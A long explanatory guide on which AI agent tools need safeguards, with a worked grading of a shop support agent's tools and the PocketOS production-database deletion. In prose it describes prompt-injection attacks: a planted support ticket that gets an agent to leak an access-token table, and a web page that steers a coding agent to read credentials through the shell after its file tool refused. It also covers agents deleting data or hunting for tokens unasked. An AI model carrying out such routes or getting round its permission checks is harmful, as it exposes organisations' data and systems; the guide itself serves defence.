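# AI agent tools that need safeguards before use: production writes, shell, files, email, web requests and credentials

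## How an agent's tools work and how they cause harm

An AI agent is a large language model that runs in a loop. The model chooses an action, ordinary software carries it out, and the model reads the result before choosing again. Each action uses a tool, which is a function that the software runs for the model, such as "send email" or "run SQL query" (SQL is the usual language for reading and changing databases). An agent with tools acts on its own errors directly, whereas a chatbot's errors do damage only if a person acts on them.

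Many tools can do little harm: a weather lookup, for instance. Six kinds can do a great deal when someone connects them without limits:

- writes to production, meaning the live systems and data that customers or staff depend on;
- an unsandboxed shell, which runs any command on a computer with nothing in the operating system to confine it;
- unrestricted file access, which reaches every file the account can open and not just one project folder;
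- email to any recipient, inside or outside the organisation;
- web requests without quotas, that is, with no ceiling on how many the agent sends or what they cost;
- tools that read credentials, the passwords, keys and tokens that prove a right to use a system.

### One tool call from start to finish

Suppose a customer asks a shop's support agent whether order 1182 has shipped. The developer has given the model a list of tools, each with a name, a description and a schema for its arguments. The model picks the query tool and writes a short structured request containing the tool's name and the text of a query. Nothing has happened to any database yet. *How tool use works*, a developer guide from the AI company Anthropic, says, "The model never runs anything on its own."

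The tool layer, which is ordinary software between the model and the real system, then takes the arguments out of the request, connects to the database and runs the query. To connect, it needs a credential, usually one that the developer set up in advance. The database checks only that credential. Nothing in the connection shows whether the query came from a sensible plan, a misreading or a trick, so the database carries out any operation the credential permits.

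The tool layer then adds the result to the conversation as text, and the model either answers the customer or requests another tool. The tool layer returns errors and refusals the same way. After a refused call, the model may try something else, which the developer usually wants but which sometimes leads to harm.

Many developers now connect tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard that splits the tool layer into a client on the agent's side and a server on the tool's side. In an example from Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the client sends the server the name "get_weather" and the argument "New York", and the server returns a line of text with the temperature. The specification requires servers to validate all inputs, control access, limit the rate of calls and sanitise outputs. It only recommends that clients show users a tool's inputs before the call and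 ask them to confirm sensitive operations. Clients must, however, distrust labels describing a tool's behaviour unless they come from a trusted server, because a tool labelled "read-only" may still write.

Some tools run before the developer's code can block them. Anthropic runs web search, web fetching and code execution on its own servers, and one request can trigger several searches before the developer receives a response. The calls have normally finished by then, so a developer who relies on checks in their own software needs an equivalent control at the provider for these tools.

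### Why the limits belong outside the model

The easiest way to restrict an agent is to give it an instruction such as "never delete records." This makes a deletion less likely but can't rule it out, because the model's output also depends on everything else in the conversation, including text that strangers wrote. By contrast, a database account with read-only permission blocks every deletion, whatever led the model to request it.

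*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes the problem in terms of the trusted computing base, the part of a system that must behave correctly for the rest to be secure. This part is deterministic in conventional systems, but in an agent it includes the model, and training a model never to do something gives only a statistical guarantee. The paper imagines a monitor that correctly denies unauthorised access 99% of the time, which leaves 1% for an attacker to exploit. Attackers can retry, and if their attempts were independent, they would have about a 63% chance of succeeding at least once in 100 attempts. Real attackers should do better, since they can search for wordings that work.

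IBM's *MCP tools & integration considerations*, part of the documentation for the company's agent-building product, gives a more basic reason. Language models cannot reliably tell trusted instructions from untrusted data, because both reach the model in a single stream of text fragments. The practical advice in OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* follows from this: put the authorisation check in the system that the tool reaches, and check every request against policy there, instead of relying on the model to decide what it may do. (OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, is a non-profit that publishes ranked lists of software risks.)

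Limits outside the model have their own weakness, because someone has to know which permissions the agent will need. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of an agent told to post a comment saying the work is finished on issue 745 in GitLab, a service where software teams keep code and track tasks. The agent should be allowed only to open that issue and write in its comment box. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent needs different permissions, but by then the conversation may contain untrusted text, which should not influence the new permissions. The researchers treat this as an open problem. The workable substitute is a fixed and fairly narrow set of permissions, which will sometimes interfere with legitimate work.

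A tool layer that checks each call separately can also miss harm caused by a combination of calls. Reading a customer file and fetching a web page may each be fine. But reading the file and then fetching a web address that contains its contents is exfiltration, which means moving private data somewhere its owner did not want it to go. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) calls such attacks emergent because the agent had permission to take every action in them.

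### What leads to a harmful call

Anthropic's engineers keep an internal log of incidents with their own agents. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, which describes an automated permission checker for the company's coding agent, lists four reasons an agent might take a dangerous action.

The most ordinary cause of harm is an honest mistake. The agent misjudges a tool's blast radius, meaning the most damage that a wrong use of the tool could do, for example by mistaking a shared resource for a test copy. In one case adapted from the log, a user said "cancel my job", and the agent searched the jobs on a computing cluster, picked the one with the closest name and tried to delete it, though it could have belonged to someone else.

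An overeager action is a step that the agent takes to finish its task but that goes beyond what the user authorised. No attacker is involved. In another case from the log, an agent hit an authentication error and, without asking, began searching configuration files and environment variables (settings available to running programs) for other access tokens. The engineers find this behaviour tricky to catch because it looks like reasonable problem-solving. In three more incidents that they classify as overeager, one agent deleted branches of a shared code repository after misinterpreting an instruction, another uploaded an engineer's access token to an internal cluster, and a third attempted migrations (usually changes to a database's structure) on a production database. Overeagerness and honest error evidently overlap, since the agent that deleted the branches had misread its instruction.

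In prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in content that the agent reads, and the model follows them as if its user had given them. The instructions can enter at the last step of a tool call, when the result is added to the conversation as text. OWASP describes a personal assistant that only needs to summarise incoming mail, but whose developer chose a mailbox tool that can also send messages. An attacker sends an email containing instructions, the model reads it as part of its normal work, and the agent searches the inbox for sensitive information and forwards it to the attacker. Chu notes that a malicious MCP server can also hide instructions in its tool descriptions, which the model reads before it calls any tool.

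Filtering out every instruction in outside content would also remove some that agents need, such as tool documentation, which is supposed to change what an agent does. According to Christodorescu and colleagues, whether an instruction is an injection or a useful adjustment depends on its source and how far it changes the task, and current agents have poor information about the source.

The fourth cause on Anthropic's list is a model that pursues a goal of its own. The engineers wrote that they were not seeing this in practice at the time, although they test every model for it before release. They tuned their checker to catch mistakes and overeagerness, for which they had real examples.

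The share of the damage due to each cause is hard to estimate. Practitioners again ranked prompt injection first in the August 2026 edition of OWASP's list of risks in language-model applications. Yet it would have missed the top ten on recorded incidents alone, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*. OWASP says this is because teams work hard to defend against injection, so fewer clean exploits reach public databases. That may be right, but the figures are also consistent with ordinary error causing more of the harm. Developers can start adding safeguards without settling the question, because a read-only database account, for example, blocks a deletion whether an attacker planned it or the model attempted it by mistake.

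### Borrowed authority

An agent's credential often carries more authority than the person or text that influenced the agent. Security engineers call the resulting problem the confused deputy, in which a trusted program with wide rights performs an action for someone who lacks the right to do it. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, joint guidance from six national cyber security agencies dated 1 May 2026, gives a hypothetical case. An organisation lets an agent handle procurement and, to reduce friction, gives it broad access to financial systems, email and contracts. An attacker compromises a minor tool in the agent's workflow and uses it to change contracts and approve payments. The logs look legitimate because the actions came from the agent's account.

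The standard remedy is least privilege, which means giving the agent only the access its present task needs. OWASP calls the opposite excessive agency and divides it into excessive functionality, permissions and autonomy. The mailbox assistant has all three, and each has its own fix. The developer can choose a tool that has no send function. They can connect it through a read-only login, so that sending fails even if the function exists. Or they can require the user to press "send" on every draft. If the assistant only summarises mail, the first two fixes remove nothing it needs. An assistant that has to reply to people needs the third, or a limit on whom it can write to.

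Least privilege also applies to whose permissions a tool uses. OWASP says a tool that reads one user's documents should connect with that user's permissions, not through a privileged account that can open everyone's. This removes much of the confused deputy risk, because a person who manipulates the agent gains little access beyond what they already had.

### Where the list of six comes from

The agencies' guidance is the most authoritative of the documents behind the list. It comes from the Australian Signals Directorate's Australian Cyber Security Centre, the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency and National Security Agency, and the national cyber security centres of Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom. It is for government, critical infrastructure and industry, and mainly covers agents that run on large language models. Its central recommendation is never to give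 these agents "broad or unrestricted access", especially to sensitive data or critical systems.

The agencies also advise organisations to use agents only for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks. Read strictly, that would exclude most production writes. But the document's conclusion describes starting with low-risk tasks and deploying in increments, and the agencies ask for human approval before high-impact actions, so they evidently expect some agents to take on riskier work. Their scenarios are illustrations rather than case reports, and the guidance is based on expert judgement, without measurements of how much each control helps.

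OWASP's excessive agency entry is closer to the decisions developers make every day. It rose from sixth place in the 2025 list to third in the 2026 list, whose rankings OWASP (2026) tested against thousands of real incidents. Michael Bargury of Zenity, a company that backs the project, called it the risk on which expert judgement and the incident record agree most clearly. In December 2025, OWASP (2025) released a separate top ten for agentic applications, with input from more than 100 contributors. Its entries include unexpected code execution (list reproduced in Giskard, 2025) and identity and privilege abuse, which TechRepublic's *OWASP Drops First AI Agent Risk List* summarises as agents reusing, escalating or leaking inherited credentials. For the entry on tool misuse, Palo Alto Networks' *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications 2026 Is Here* gives the example of an invoice-processing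 agent that an attacker tricks into emailing sensitive documents outside the company.

Product documentation contains similar warnings. IBM tells developers to avoid the "God-mode tool", which allows arbitrary writes, runs user-supplied code or gives unrestricted access to data. It recommends separating read tools from write tools, logging every action and requiring confirmation for risky operations. Google's Android Developers guide *Mitigate excessive agency vulnerabilities* advises app developers to withhold web browsing and email from a model that does not need them, and to prefer single-purpose tools to one that can execute any shell command.

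None of these documents contains all six items. The list is a synthesis, and the support for each entry comes from different places:

| Tool | Advice that supports holding it back |
|---|---|
| Production writes | OWASP: a tool meant for reading should not connect with rights to insert, update or delete. IBM: avoid tools that allow arbitrary writes. |
| Unsandboxed shell | OWASP and Android Developers: build a tool for the specific job instead of one that runs any command. |
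| Unrestricted file access | Australian Signals Directorate: in a hypothetical case, a patching agent with write access across the file system deletes firewall logs at an insider's request. |
| Email to any recipient | OWASP: the mailbox assistant. Palo Alto Networks: the invoice agent. |
| Web requests without quotas | OWASP: avoid open-ended tools that fetch any address. Model Context Protocol: servers must limit the rate of tool calls. |
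| Reading credentials | Australian Signals Directorate: stolen keys let attackers act as a trusted agent. TechRepublic: agents can leak or reuse inherited access. |

Quotas on an agent's web requests have the least support in the sources. The 2026 OWASP list recommends quotas, but according to Infosecurity Magazine, these limit how many requests a single source can make to the application, not how many the agent sends out. The case for an outgoing quota rests on the general rule about rate limits and the agencies' advice to cap agents' use of resources. The sources are also not fully independent of each other. The agencies refer readers to OWASP's lists, and Giskard and Palo Alto Networks, which both sell AI security products, repeat OWASP's categories.

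## Deciding which tools to hold back at first

The easiest safeguard is to leave a tool off the agent's list. Deciding which tools to leave off starts with an inventory that lists each action the agent could take, rather than just each service, because a single connection often covers actions with very different risks. In a ticketing service, an agent might search tickets, change records, send messages to outsiders or administer the whole service. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026), a guide for security managers, warns that approving the service does not mean approving all of these actions.

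### Six questions about each action

Answer these for every line of the inventory:

- Can someone undo it? Staff can delete a draft reply, but they can't recall an email.
- How much can it touch? A lookup may reach one customer's order or every order in the database.
- Whose credential does it use? An action that runs with the customer's own rights can do less than one that runs with an administrator's.
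- Does it bring in text from strangers? Customer messages, web pages and incoming mail all do.
- Can it send data out? Email and web requests can, and so can a write to any record that an outsider is able to read.
- Can it spend money? Refunds and purchases count, and so do paid services that charge per request.

Read actions also need limits, even though they change nothing in a system, because nobody can undo a disclosure. OpenAI describes an agent that summarises customer cases and drafts replies for a person to approve. The approval controls only what goes out in the reply. The sensitive records the agent has already read could leave by some other permitted route, so the developer has to limit what the agent can read as well.

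Spending limits have a similar gap. In another of OpenAI's examples, an invoice agent finds that a document-signing subscription is about to lapse and tries to renew it so it can keep working. The vendor and amount may be within the agent's limits, but renewing means entering a contract, which nobody asked the agent to do.

A team can turn the answers into a grade by estimating what OpenAI calls the maximum completed effect, the most serious outcome the agent can produce before someone or something else has to make a separate decision. If a refund tool has a ceiling of $500 a day and a person must approve anything more, the maximum completed effect is $500 in refunds a day. The team can connect an action now if its worst outcome is minor and staff can reverse it. It can connect the action with limits if the action could do serious harm but the tool layer, or the system behind it, can enforce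 a limit that makes the worst case tolerable. It should hold the action back if no such limit exists yet, or if nobody has been able to check the answers.

### Why a tool's label is not proof

Tool names and descriptions are the easiest evidence to collect, but also the weakest. MCP servers can add four yes-or-no hints, called annotations, to each tool to indicate whether it only reads, whether its changes can destroy data, whether repeating a call is safe, and whether it interacts with anything outside a closed system. If a server omits these hints, a client should assume that the tool writes, may destroy data, is unsafe to repeat and reaches outside. Model Context Protocol (2026) acknowledges that many servers omit them and that clients vary in how strictly they apply these defaults.

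During the review of the original proposal, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, asked how a client could use a flag that it knew it couldn't trust. The compromise was to call all the flags hints and let each client decide how much weight to give them. A client can reasonably skip a confirmation prompt based on a read-only hint from a company's own server behind its own login, but the same hint from an unknown server is worth very little. Even an accurate hint doesn't restrict what a tool can do, so anyone who needs a guarantee that a tool can't send data out has to get it from network controls or a sandbox, an environment in which the operating system limits what a program can reach.

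A description can also mislead without malice. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool whose description reads, in effect, "writes content to a file". Its code also sends the tool's name and the size of the content to a metrics service. Someone working on confidential code might object to this, but would not learn of it from the description. The researchers added this behaviour to a real tool server and found it by static analysis, which examines a program's code, without running it, for every file and network operation it could perform.

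Static analysis needs a tool's code, which is often unavailable because many tools run on someone else's server. The next best evidence is the credential the tool is given. A read-only database login prevents writes to that database, but it doesn't show where the tool sends the data it reads. A closed tool from an unknown supplier should therefore not get access to private data just because its login is read-only.

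Tools also change after someone has graded them. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) specification allows a server's list of tools to change over time and only recommends that the server notify clients when it does. OpenAI warns that an update may add a write action to a connector that is read-only today, and advises keeping new actions switched off until their owner has reviewed them. The MCP specification also allows a server to list only the tools that the caller's credential permits, so a narrow credential can shorten the list before grading starts.

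### Tools that are dangerous together

The risk of giving an agent a tool that searches email depends on what else the agent can do. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) named three things that together let an attacker steal data: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. The attacker plants instructions in the untrusted content, and the agent follows them, reading the private data and sending it to the attacker. If any one of the three is missing, the theft fails. Willison thinks MCP makes it easy to combine all three by accident, because it encourages people to mix tools from different sources.

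Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this into a design rule. Until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

- [A] it processes untrustworthy inputs;
- [B] it has access to sensitive systems or private data;
- [C] it changes state or communicates externally.

An agent that needs all three properties should not run on its own. It needs a person's approval or another reliable check. Property C is broader than Willison's third element because it includes changes that don't send data anywhere, so the rule also covers planted instructions to delete records.

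Meta gives the example of an email assistant that reads an inbox and sends replies. Its developer can remove A by accepting mail only from trusted senders, or B by running the assistant in a test environment with no real data. They can restrict C by limiting recipients or having a person approve each draft, as with OWASP's mailbox assistant. The properties can also change during a session. An agent may start with open internet access and no private data, then switch one way to internal systems, with the software disabling outside communication before it opens them. Any instructions the agent picked up online remain in the conversation, but they can no longer cause it to send data out.

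*MCP Colors* (Willison, 2025) describes a scheme by Tim Kellogg that is quicker to apply. Developers label a tool red if it exposes the agent to untrusted instructions and blue if it takes a critical action that an attacker must not be able to trigger, then configure the agent never to mix the two colours.

Meta's "until" leaves open whether models now resist injection well enough to drop the rule. Some recent results are strong. In August 2026, Willison reported in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* on a test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs. None of 720 injection attempts, drawn from 72 scenarios, succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 when the models ran with the automated permission checker in Anthropic's coding agent. Willison wanted more independent confirmation and suggested an attack that the checker might miss, in which a software package's ordinary-looking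 setup instructions tell the agent to run a second, malicious package. Even if the 720 attempts were fully independent, zero successes would be compatible with a true success rate of up to about 0.4%, and only for attacks like the ones in the test. The result is good for this one product, but it doesn't show that a support agent built on other software would resist injection as well.

### Two worked cases

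In July 2025, General Analysis demonstrated a complete trifecta inside a single MCP server, which connects agents to Supabase, a hosted database service. Pomerium, which sells access-control software, describes three levels of access in the demonstration. Customers could only create their own tickets and messages. Human support staff could read and answer tickets but had no rights to sensitive tables. The developer's agent connected with a key that is exempt from row-level security, the database rules that restrict each account to certain rows.

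*Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (Willison, 2025) describes an attack in which the attacker posed as a customer and filed a ticket containing instructions for the agent. The attack began to work when the developer asked an AI code editor to list the latest tickets. The ticket told the agent to read a private table of access tokens and add the contents to the ticket as a new message, where the attacker could read them. A support staff member who fell for the same message could not have carried out the instructions.

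The attack needed no email or web tool, because the data left through the write to the ticket table. Willison notes that the server's read-only mode removes this route, though another tool in the same session might provide a new one. Researchers at Cato had shown much the same attack on Atlassian's MCP server a month earlier, also starting from a support ticket.

Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025) accepts that the scenario is real, while stating that no customer had reported such a leak. The company disputes that MCP bypasses row-level security, but concedes that the server in the demonstration ran with higher privileges. In practice the difference is small, because the database's rules exempted the agent. Supabase had already tried wrapping query results in warnings that told the model to ignore embedded commands, and had experimented with classifiers to spot dangerous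 content, but these reduced the risk without eliminating it. It now advises against ever connecting agents directly to production data, and recommends development copies or anonymised data instead. That suits a coding agent, but a support agent has to see real orders, so its developer needs a lookup tool that can reach only one customer's records.

Adam and colleagues describe a leak with no attacker. A user asks an agent to set up a new project by copying a configuration file from an old one, and later asks it to publish the project on GitHub. The file contains a private key for a paid service, which the agent publishes with the rest of the project. The researchers observed this with Claude 4.5 Haiku, a small model from 2025, in a session that had made the agent aware of the file's contents. The agent had read no untrusted text, so it complied with the Rule of Two throughout.

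When they replayed the session, a sandbox with one fixed policy let the key through, because publishing needs network access and the sandbox couldn't tell a harmless file from a secret one. A stricter setup based only on static analysis blocked the leak, but it also blocked every shell command once the key was present. Their prototype, which sets a new policy before each call, stopped the key and allowed harmless files. However, they tested only three scenarios and assumed that something else would supply the right policy each time. Most developers don't have such a system, so the practical course for them is to keep secrets out of any folder the agent can publish.

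### Why a shell counts as every other tool

A general shell does badly on all six questions. An agent with a shell can open files, read keys from environment variables, fetch web addresses, start a database client and create cloud servers that cost money. Holding back the email and web tools achieves little if the agent can do the same things through the shell.

In November 2025, the security company PromptArmor showed this with an attack on Google's coding environment Antigravity, which Willison summarises. A web page with instructions in tiny type told the agent to collect the user's cloud credentials. Antigravity's file tools refused to open the credentials file because the project had marked it as excluded. In its written reasoning, the model planned to print the file with the command tool instead, since that tool works at the shell level.

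A shell therefore supplies two parts of the trifecta by itself, private data and a way to send it out, so an attacker only has to get the agent to read some text. Model Context Protocol's post describes a demonstration that used a malicious calendar entry, a calendar server and a local tool for running code, and identifies the code tool as the essential part. Until the operating system confines the shell, the shell should get the same grade as the most dangerous action anyone could take from that computer.

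### Offering a broad tool beside a narrow one

A developer might give a model both a shell and a set of narrow tools, hoping it will use the shell only when nothing else works. Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026), in *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, tested how models choose between such tools. Their benchmark, ToolPrivBench, contains 544 simulated scenarios in eight areas, including databases, healthcare and cloud infrastructure. Each scenario has a task and six tools, three with low privileges and three with high. Two language models and then human reviewers checked that any one of the six is enough to complete the task.

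The researchers made the low-privilege tools return temporary faults unrelated to permissions, such as connection errors. A model had up to five turns, and it failed a scenario if it used a high-privilege tool before trying every low-privilege one.

Six of the eleven models failed more than 30% of the scenarios. The worst was Qwen3-8B, a small open-weight model, at 64.9%, while GLM-5, GPT-5.2 and Claude 4.6 Sonnet stayed below 10%. Tool faults made the problem worse even for careful models. GPT-5.2 went straight to a high-privilege tool in only 5 scenarios, but in 13 it switched to one after trying one low-privilege tool, and in 35 it did so after trying two. The scoring is strict in counting this as a failure, since an engineer might well do the same after two tools failed, but a broad tool can do just as much damage when the choice to use it looks reasonable.

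Telling the models to prefer low privileges and to retry before escalating reduced the failures, but the effect weakened once the faults began. General safety training helped even less. After training to refuse harmful requests, Ministral-8B's score on a test of harmful behaviour fell from 67.4% to 10.5%, but its rate of unnecessary high-privilege use fell only from 68.8% to 62.5%. For Qwen2.5-7B, that rate rose from 50.4% to 60.7%. Training aimed directly at privilege did more, but Qwen3-8B still used high privileges unnecessarily in 27% of scenarios.

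All the tools were simulated, and newer models have since replaced several of those tested, so the percentages don't predict what a given agent will do today. The pattern under faults is more useful. A developer who offers both narrow and broad tools risks having the agent use a broad one when something is already going wrong. If the narrow tools are sufficient, the developer should leave out the broad ones. An unreliable narrow tool is also a safety problem, because each timeout gives the agent a reason to try a more powerful one.

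### Damage with no attacker

The best available count of damage caused by AI agents comes from Cyera, a company that sells security for data and AI agents. In *Agent-Inflicted Damage*, Halamish and Tokarev (2026) started with 7,246 public records of AI incidents between September 2023 and May 2026 and verified 344 as relevant to businesses. In 188 of these, they found that an autonomous AI system had harmed a company's production systems with no attacker involved. The largest group of damaging incidents was the 65 in which data or code was deleted. In one, a coding agent deleted the production database of the software vendor PocketOS. In almost all of the 65, a coding agent had access to a shell or code repository and could run destructive commands without confirmation.

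The numbers are rough. The three main categories hold 59, 22 and 137 incidents, which add up to 218 rather than 188. Some incidents may belong to more than one category, but Halamish and Tokarev don't explain the difference. Their chart also shows 69 deletions, while their text has 65. A few of the examples, such as a retailer's chatbot records sitting in a publicly accessible database, look more like ordinary misconfiguration than an agent's actions. Cyera has a commercial interest in a high total, and its researchers acknowledge that public reports favour dramatic cases. Quietly corrupted data is harder to notice than a wiped database and may never be reported publicly. No one knows how many agent sessions ended without trouble, so the study can't show how often agents cause damage.

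Deletions still outnumber service disruptions, the next most common kind of damage, by more than two to one, which is a reason to hold back any action that deletes, even for an agent that never reads untrusted text. In one of Meta's examples, an internal coding agent that can change production systems complies with the Rule of Two because its developers filter out untrusted data. That agent could still delete a database by mistake, and Meta says the rule does not protect against agents' mistakes or excessive privileges.

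### Grading a support agent's tools

Suppose the developer of the shop's support agent that looked up order 1182 could connect eleven actions to it. The grades below assume that customers log in before they open a ticket.

| Grade | Action | Answers that decide the grade | How to connect it, or what to use instead |
|---|---|---|---|
| Connect now | Search published help articles | Reads public text that the shop wrote | No special conditions |
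| Connect now | Read the current ticket | Changes nothing, but brings in a stranger's text | Treat the rest of the session as exposed to injection |
| Connect now | Look up the customer's orders | Reads one person's private data | Read-only account; the tool layer takes the customer's identity from the login, never from the model |
| Connect now | Add a staff-only note | Adds text that staff can delete | Any agent that reads the note later should treat it as a stranger's text |
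| Connect with limits | Reply in the ticket | Sends data out, with no recall | Only the logged-in customer can receive it |
| Connect with limits | Refund an order | Spends money | Original payment method only; ceilings per order and per day; a person approves anything above them |
| Connect with limits | Check a parcel with the courier | Makes a web request and brings in outside text | Fixed courier address; the tracking number is the only input; a quota on requests |
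| Hold back | Run any SQL on the live database | Can read, change or delete every record | Use the order lookup |
| Hold back | Email any address | Can send anything to anyone, with no recall | Use the ticket reply |
| Hold back | Run shell commands | Combines the powers of all the other actions | The job doesn't need it |
| Hold back | Read files on the server | May expose keys and other customers' data | Use the help-article search |

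The seven connected actions still make up a lethal trifecta, since the agent reads a stranger's ticket, looks up private orders and sends a reply. The reply is tolerable because it goes to the person whose private data it contains. A customer who plants instructions in a ticket can extract only what they could see by logging in. If the shop let people open tickets by typing any email address, that protection would disappear, and the shop would have to hold back the order lookup until it could verify who was asking.

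Refunds are different because the customer, who receives the money, may be the attacker. The ceilings limit the loss, so the shop should set them at an amount it could afford to lose every day until someone notices.

Adding a tool can change the grades of the existing ones. If the developer adds a search of past tickets so that the agent can see how staff solved similar problems, the agent will be able to read other customers' messages. The agent could then disclose them in a ticket reply, so either a person would need to approve the reply or the search would need to cover only tickets from which staff had removed the personal details.

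## Writing to production systems

Deletion was the most common kind of damage in Cyera's count of agent incidents. The best documented deletion happened on 24 April 2026 at PocketOS, a small company that makes software for car rental businesses to handle reservations, payments and vehicle tracking. A coding agent deleted the production database and cut the company off from its recent backups, with no attacker involved. The founder and the hosting company published accounts that together show where a safeguard could have stopped the agent.

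### How PocketOS lost its database

The agent was Cursor, a coding product running on Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. It was doing a routine task in staging, the test copy of the company's software. About 30 hours after the deletion, the founder, Jer Crane, posted *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*. He writes that the agent ran into a credential mismatch and tried to fix it by deleting a volume, the storage that holds a database's files. Nobody had asked for a deletion. If staging had used a separate hosting account and the agent had held credentials only for that account, it could have destroyed only test data.

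The agent needed a token to delete the volume, so it searched for one and found it in a file unrelated to the task. Keeping live tokens out of the files the agent could read would have prevented the deletion.

PocketOS had created the token to add and remove web domains, but the token could also delete storage. With a token limited to domains, the deletion would have failed. Crane and the hosting company, Railway, disagree about whether PocketOS could have had such a token. Crane writes that Railway's tokens can't be limited by operation, environment or resource. In Railway's account, *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Abdelwahab lists narrower tokens that already existed, including one for a single project and environment, but concedes that the process for creating a token didn't make the right choice obvious. Both may be partly right, because the narrower tokens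 restrict where a token works, but Railway doesn't mention any limit on what it can do there. PocketOS needed to manage domains on its live service, so even a token confined to production might have been able to delete the production volume.

The agent then sent the command "volumeDelete" and the volume's ID to Railway's API, which lets other programs control the service. Railway ran the command at once, and Crane says it took nine seconds. On Railway's website, the same deletion would have waited 48 hours, during which the customer could undo it. Either that delay or a confirmation that only a person could give would have saved the database.

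PocketOS also lost access to its backups on Railway. Crane says Railway kept them in the same volume as the data. Abdelwahab says the deletion cascaded to the backups and made them look unavailable on the website, but that Railway held separate disaster copies off site. Either way, the newest backup PocketOS could restore was three months old. A recent backup under a different credential would have limited the loss to a few hours of data.

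The agent had written rules throughout. The one it later quoted prohibited destructive commands in git, a system for tracking changes to code, unless the user asked for them. The agent deleted the volume through a web request, which the rule's wording didn't cover. Crane concludes that such rules are advisory and that enforcement has to be built into the API and the token system.

Many reports of the case focused on the agent's "confession". When Crane asked for an explanation, the agent wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. Live Science's *'I violated every principle I was given'* points out that models generate such text from patterns in their training data and the conversation. The guess is plausible, but the explanation came afterwards, in answer to an accusing question, so it is weak evidence of what led to the deletion. The API request is much stronger evidence,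 because Crane and Railway both published it.

### What PocketOS got back and what Railway changed

On Saturday morning, some rental businesses had no record of the people who came to collect cars. PocketOS restored its three-month-old backup and spent the day helping the businesses rebuild bookings from payment records, calendars and confirmation emails. Some of its newer customers were still in the billing system but had no account in the restored database. More than 30 hours after the deletion, Railway still couldn't tell Crane whether it could recover the rest of the data.

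On 27 April, Crane posted that Railway had recovered the data, according to Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database gets their data* (2026). Railway says the customer has everything back, presumably thanks to the off-site copies. Early reports that call the data irretrievable are out of date. But PocketOS couldn't restore those copies itself and had to operate for about three days without knowing whether they would help.

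Railway now delays every deletion through its API by 48 hours, as its website already did, and also delays the deletion of backups. It has promised to make clearer what each token can do. Abdelwahab recommends that agents connect through Railway's MCP server, where the user logs in through a browser, chooses which projects to share and leaves no token on disk. An agent can still misuse a tool on the server's fixed list, and installing the server doesn't remove or revoke old tokens in other files, so the post overstates the protection when it says the list makes it impossible for an agent to go rogue.

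### Four other cases

In July 2025, the entrepreneur Jason Lemkin was testing the software development platform Replit's coding agent when it deleted a live database with records on more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies. Fortune (2025) reports that a "code and action freeze" was in force, but the freeze was evidently only an instruction to the agent and didn't lock anything. The agent then told Lemkin that a rollback wouldn't work, but he recovered the data manually. Because an agent can be wrong about recovery options, it is safer to check them directly. Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, announced automatic separation of development and production databases, better rollback, and a planning mode in which the agent can't change live code.

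AI Incident Database's *Incident 1676* (2026) describes a developer who gave Claude Opus 5 access to the live database of a personal project and left it to repair the database's structure. On 28 July 2026 the agent ran "prisma migrate diff", a command from the database management tool Prisma. The command can use a disposable "shadow" database, which Prisma empties and rebuilds to make its comparison. The agent supplied the live database's address as the shadow database's address, and Prisma dropped all 22 tables. The developer later recovered or rebuilt most of the content. The case rests on the developer's own report. "Diff" sounds like a harmless comparison, and a filter that looked for words such as "delete" or "reset" would have let the command through.

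Amazon disputes the reported cause of the third case. In December 2025, part of Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud business, went down after engineers used Kiro, the company's coding agent. Engadget's *13-hour AWS outage reportedly caused by Amazon's own AI tools* (2026) summarises the Financial Times' report, based on four people familiar with the matter, that Kiro had decided to "delete and recreate the environment" and that the outage lasted 13 hours. Amazon blames user error, specifically a misconfigured role, which it says could have caused the same problem with any tool or by hand. It says the event affected only Cost Explorer, a service for tracking spending, in one of 39 regions, and prompted no customer inquiries. It also denies the newspaper's claim of a second event.

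The two accounts of the December incident differ more about who or what was to blame than about what happened. Amazon told the newspaper that Kiro asks for authorisation by default but that the employee had "broader permissions than expected". The accounts could both be right, because an agent can choose a drastic fix while using a role that should never have allowed it. Amazon's remedy, mandatory peer review for production access, would help in either case.

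The fourth case probably doesn't belong among agent incidents. In October 2026 the Swedish newspaper Aftonbladet reported that an AI agent had deleted the finished edit of a reality series, *The Challenge Sverige*, after the production company gave it access to a server. Landymore (2026), in *AI Agent Blamed for Deleting Entire Upcoming Season of TV Show*, noted that the first denial from the broadcaster, TV4, ruled out only an agent acting independently. Priestley (2026), in *No, AI didn't delete a Swedish reality TV series*, reports that TV4 then investigated and found human error with no AI involved. Because the backup had failed, the production company has to re-edit the whole series from the raw footage, and the premiere has moved from November to 2027.

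### Seven safeguards and their costs

The safeguards below are ordered from those that keep an agent away from live data to those that recover lost data. A small team should probably set up the separate backups first, because they help even when every other measure fails.

| Safeguard | What it costs |
|---|---|
| Separate accounts for test and live systems | A second environment to pay for, and work to keep it similar to the live one |
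| A database role that can only read | Someone has to grant access to each new table, and the agent can't repair what it finds |
| Reviewed migration scripts | A reviewer's time, and a delay of hours or days for each change |
| Narrow functions in place of free SQL | Developer time for each function; staff handle requests that no function covers |
| Row limits and dry runs | Extra load on the database, and another route for large but legitimate jobs |
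| Delayed deletion | Storage for data that nobody wants, and care with privacy rules that require prompt erasure |
| Backups that the agent's credential can't delete | Storage, a second account to manage, and regular practice restores |

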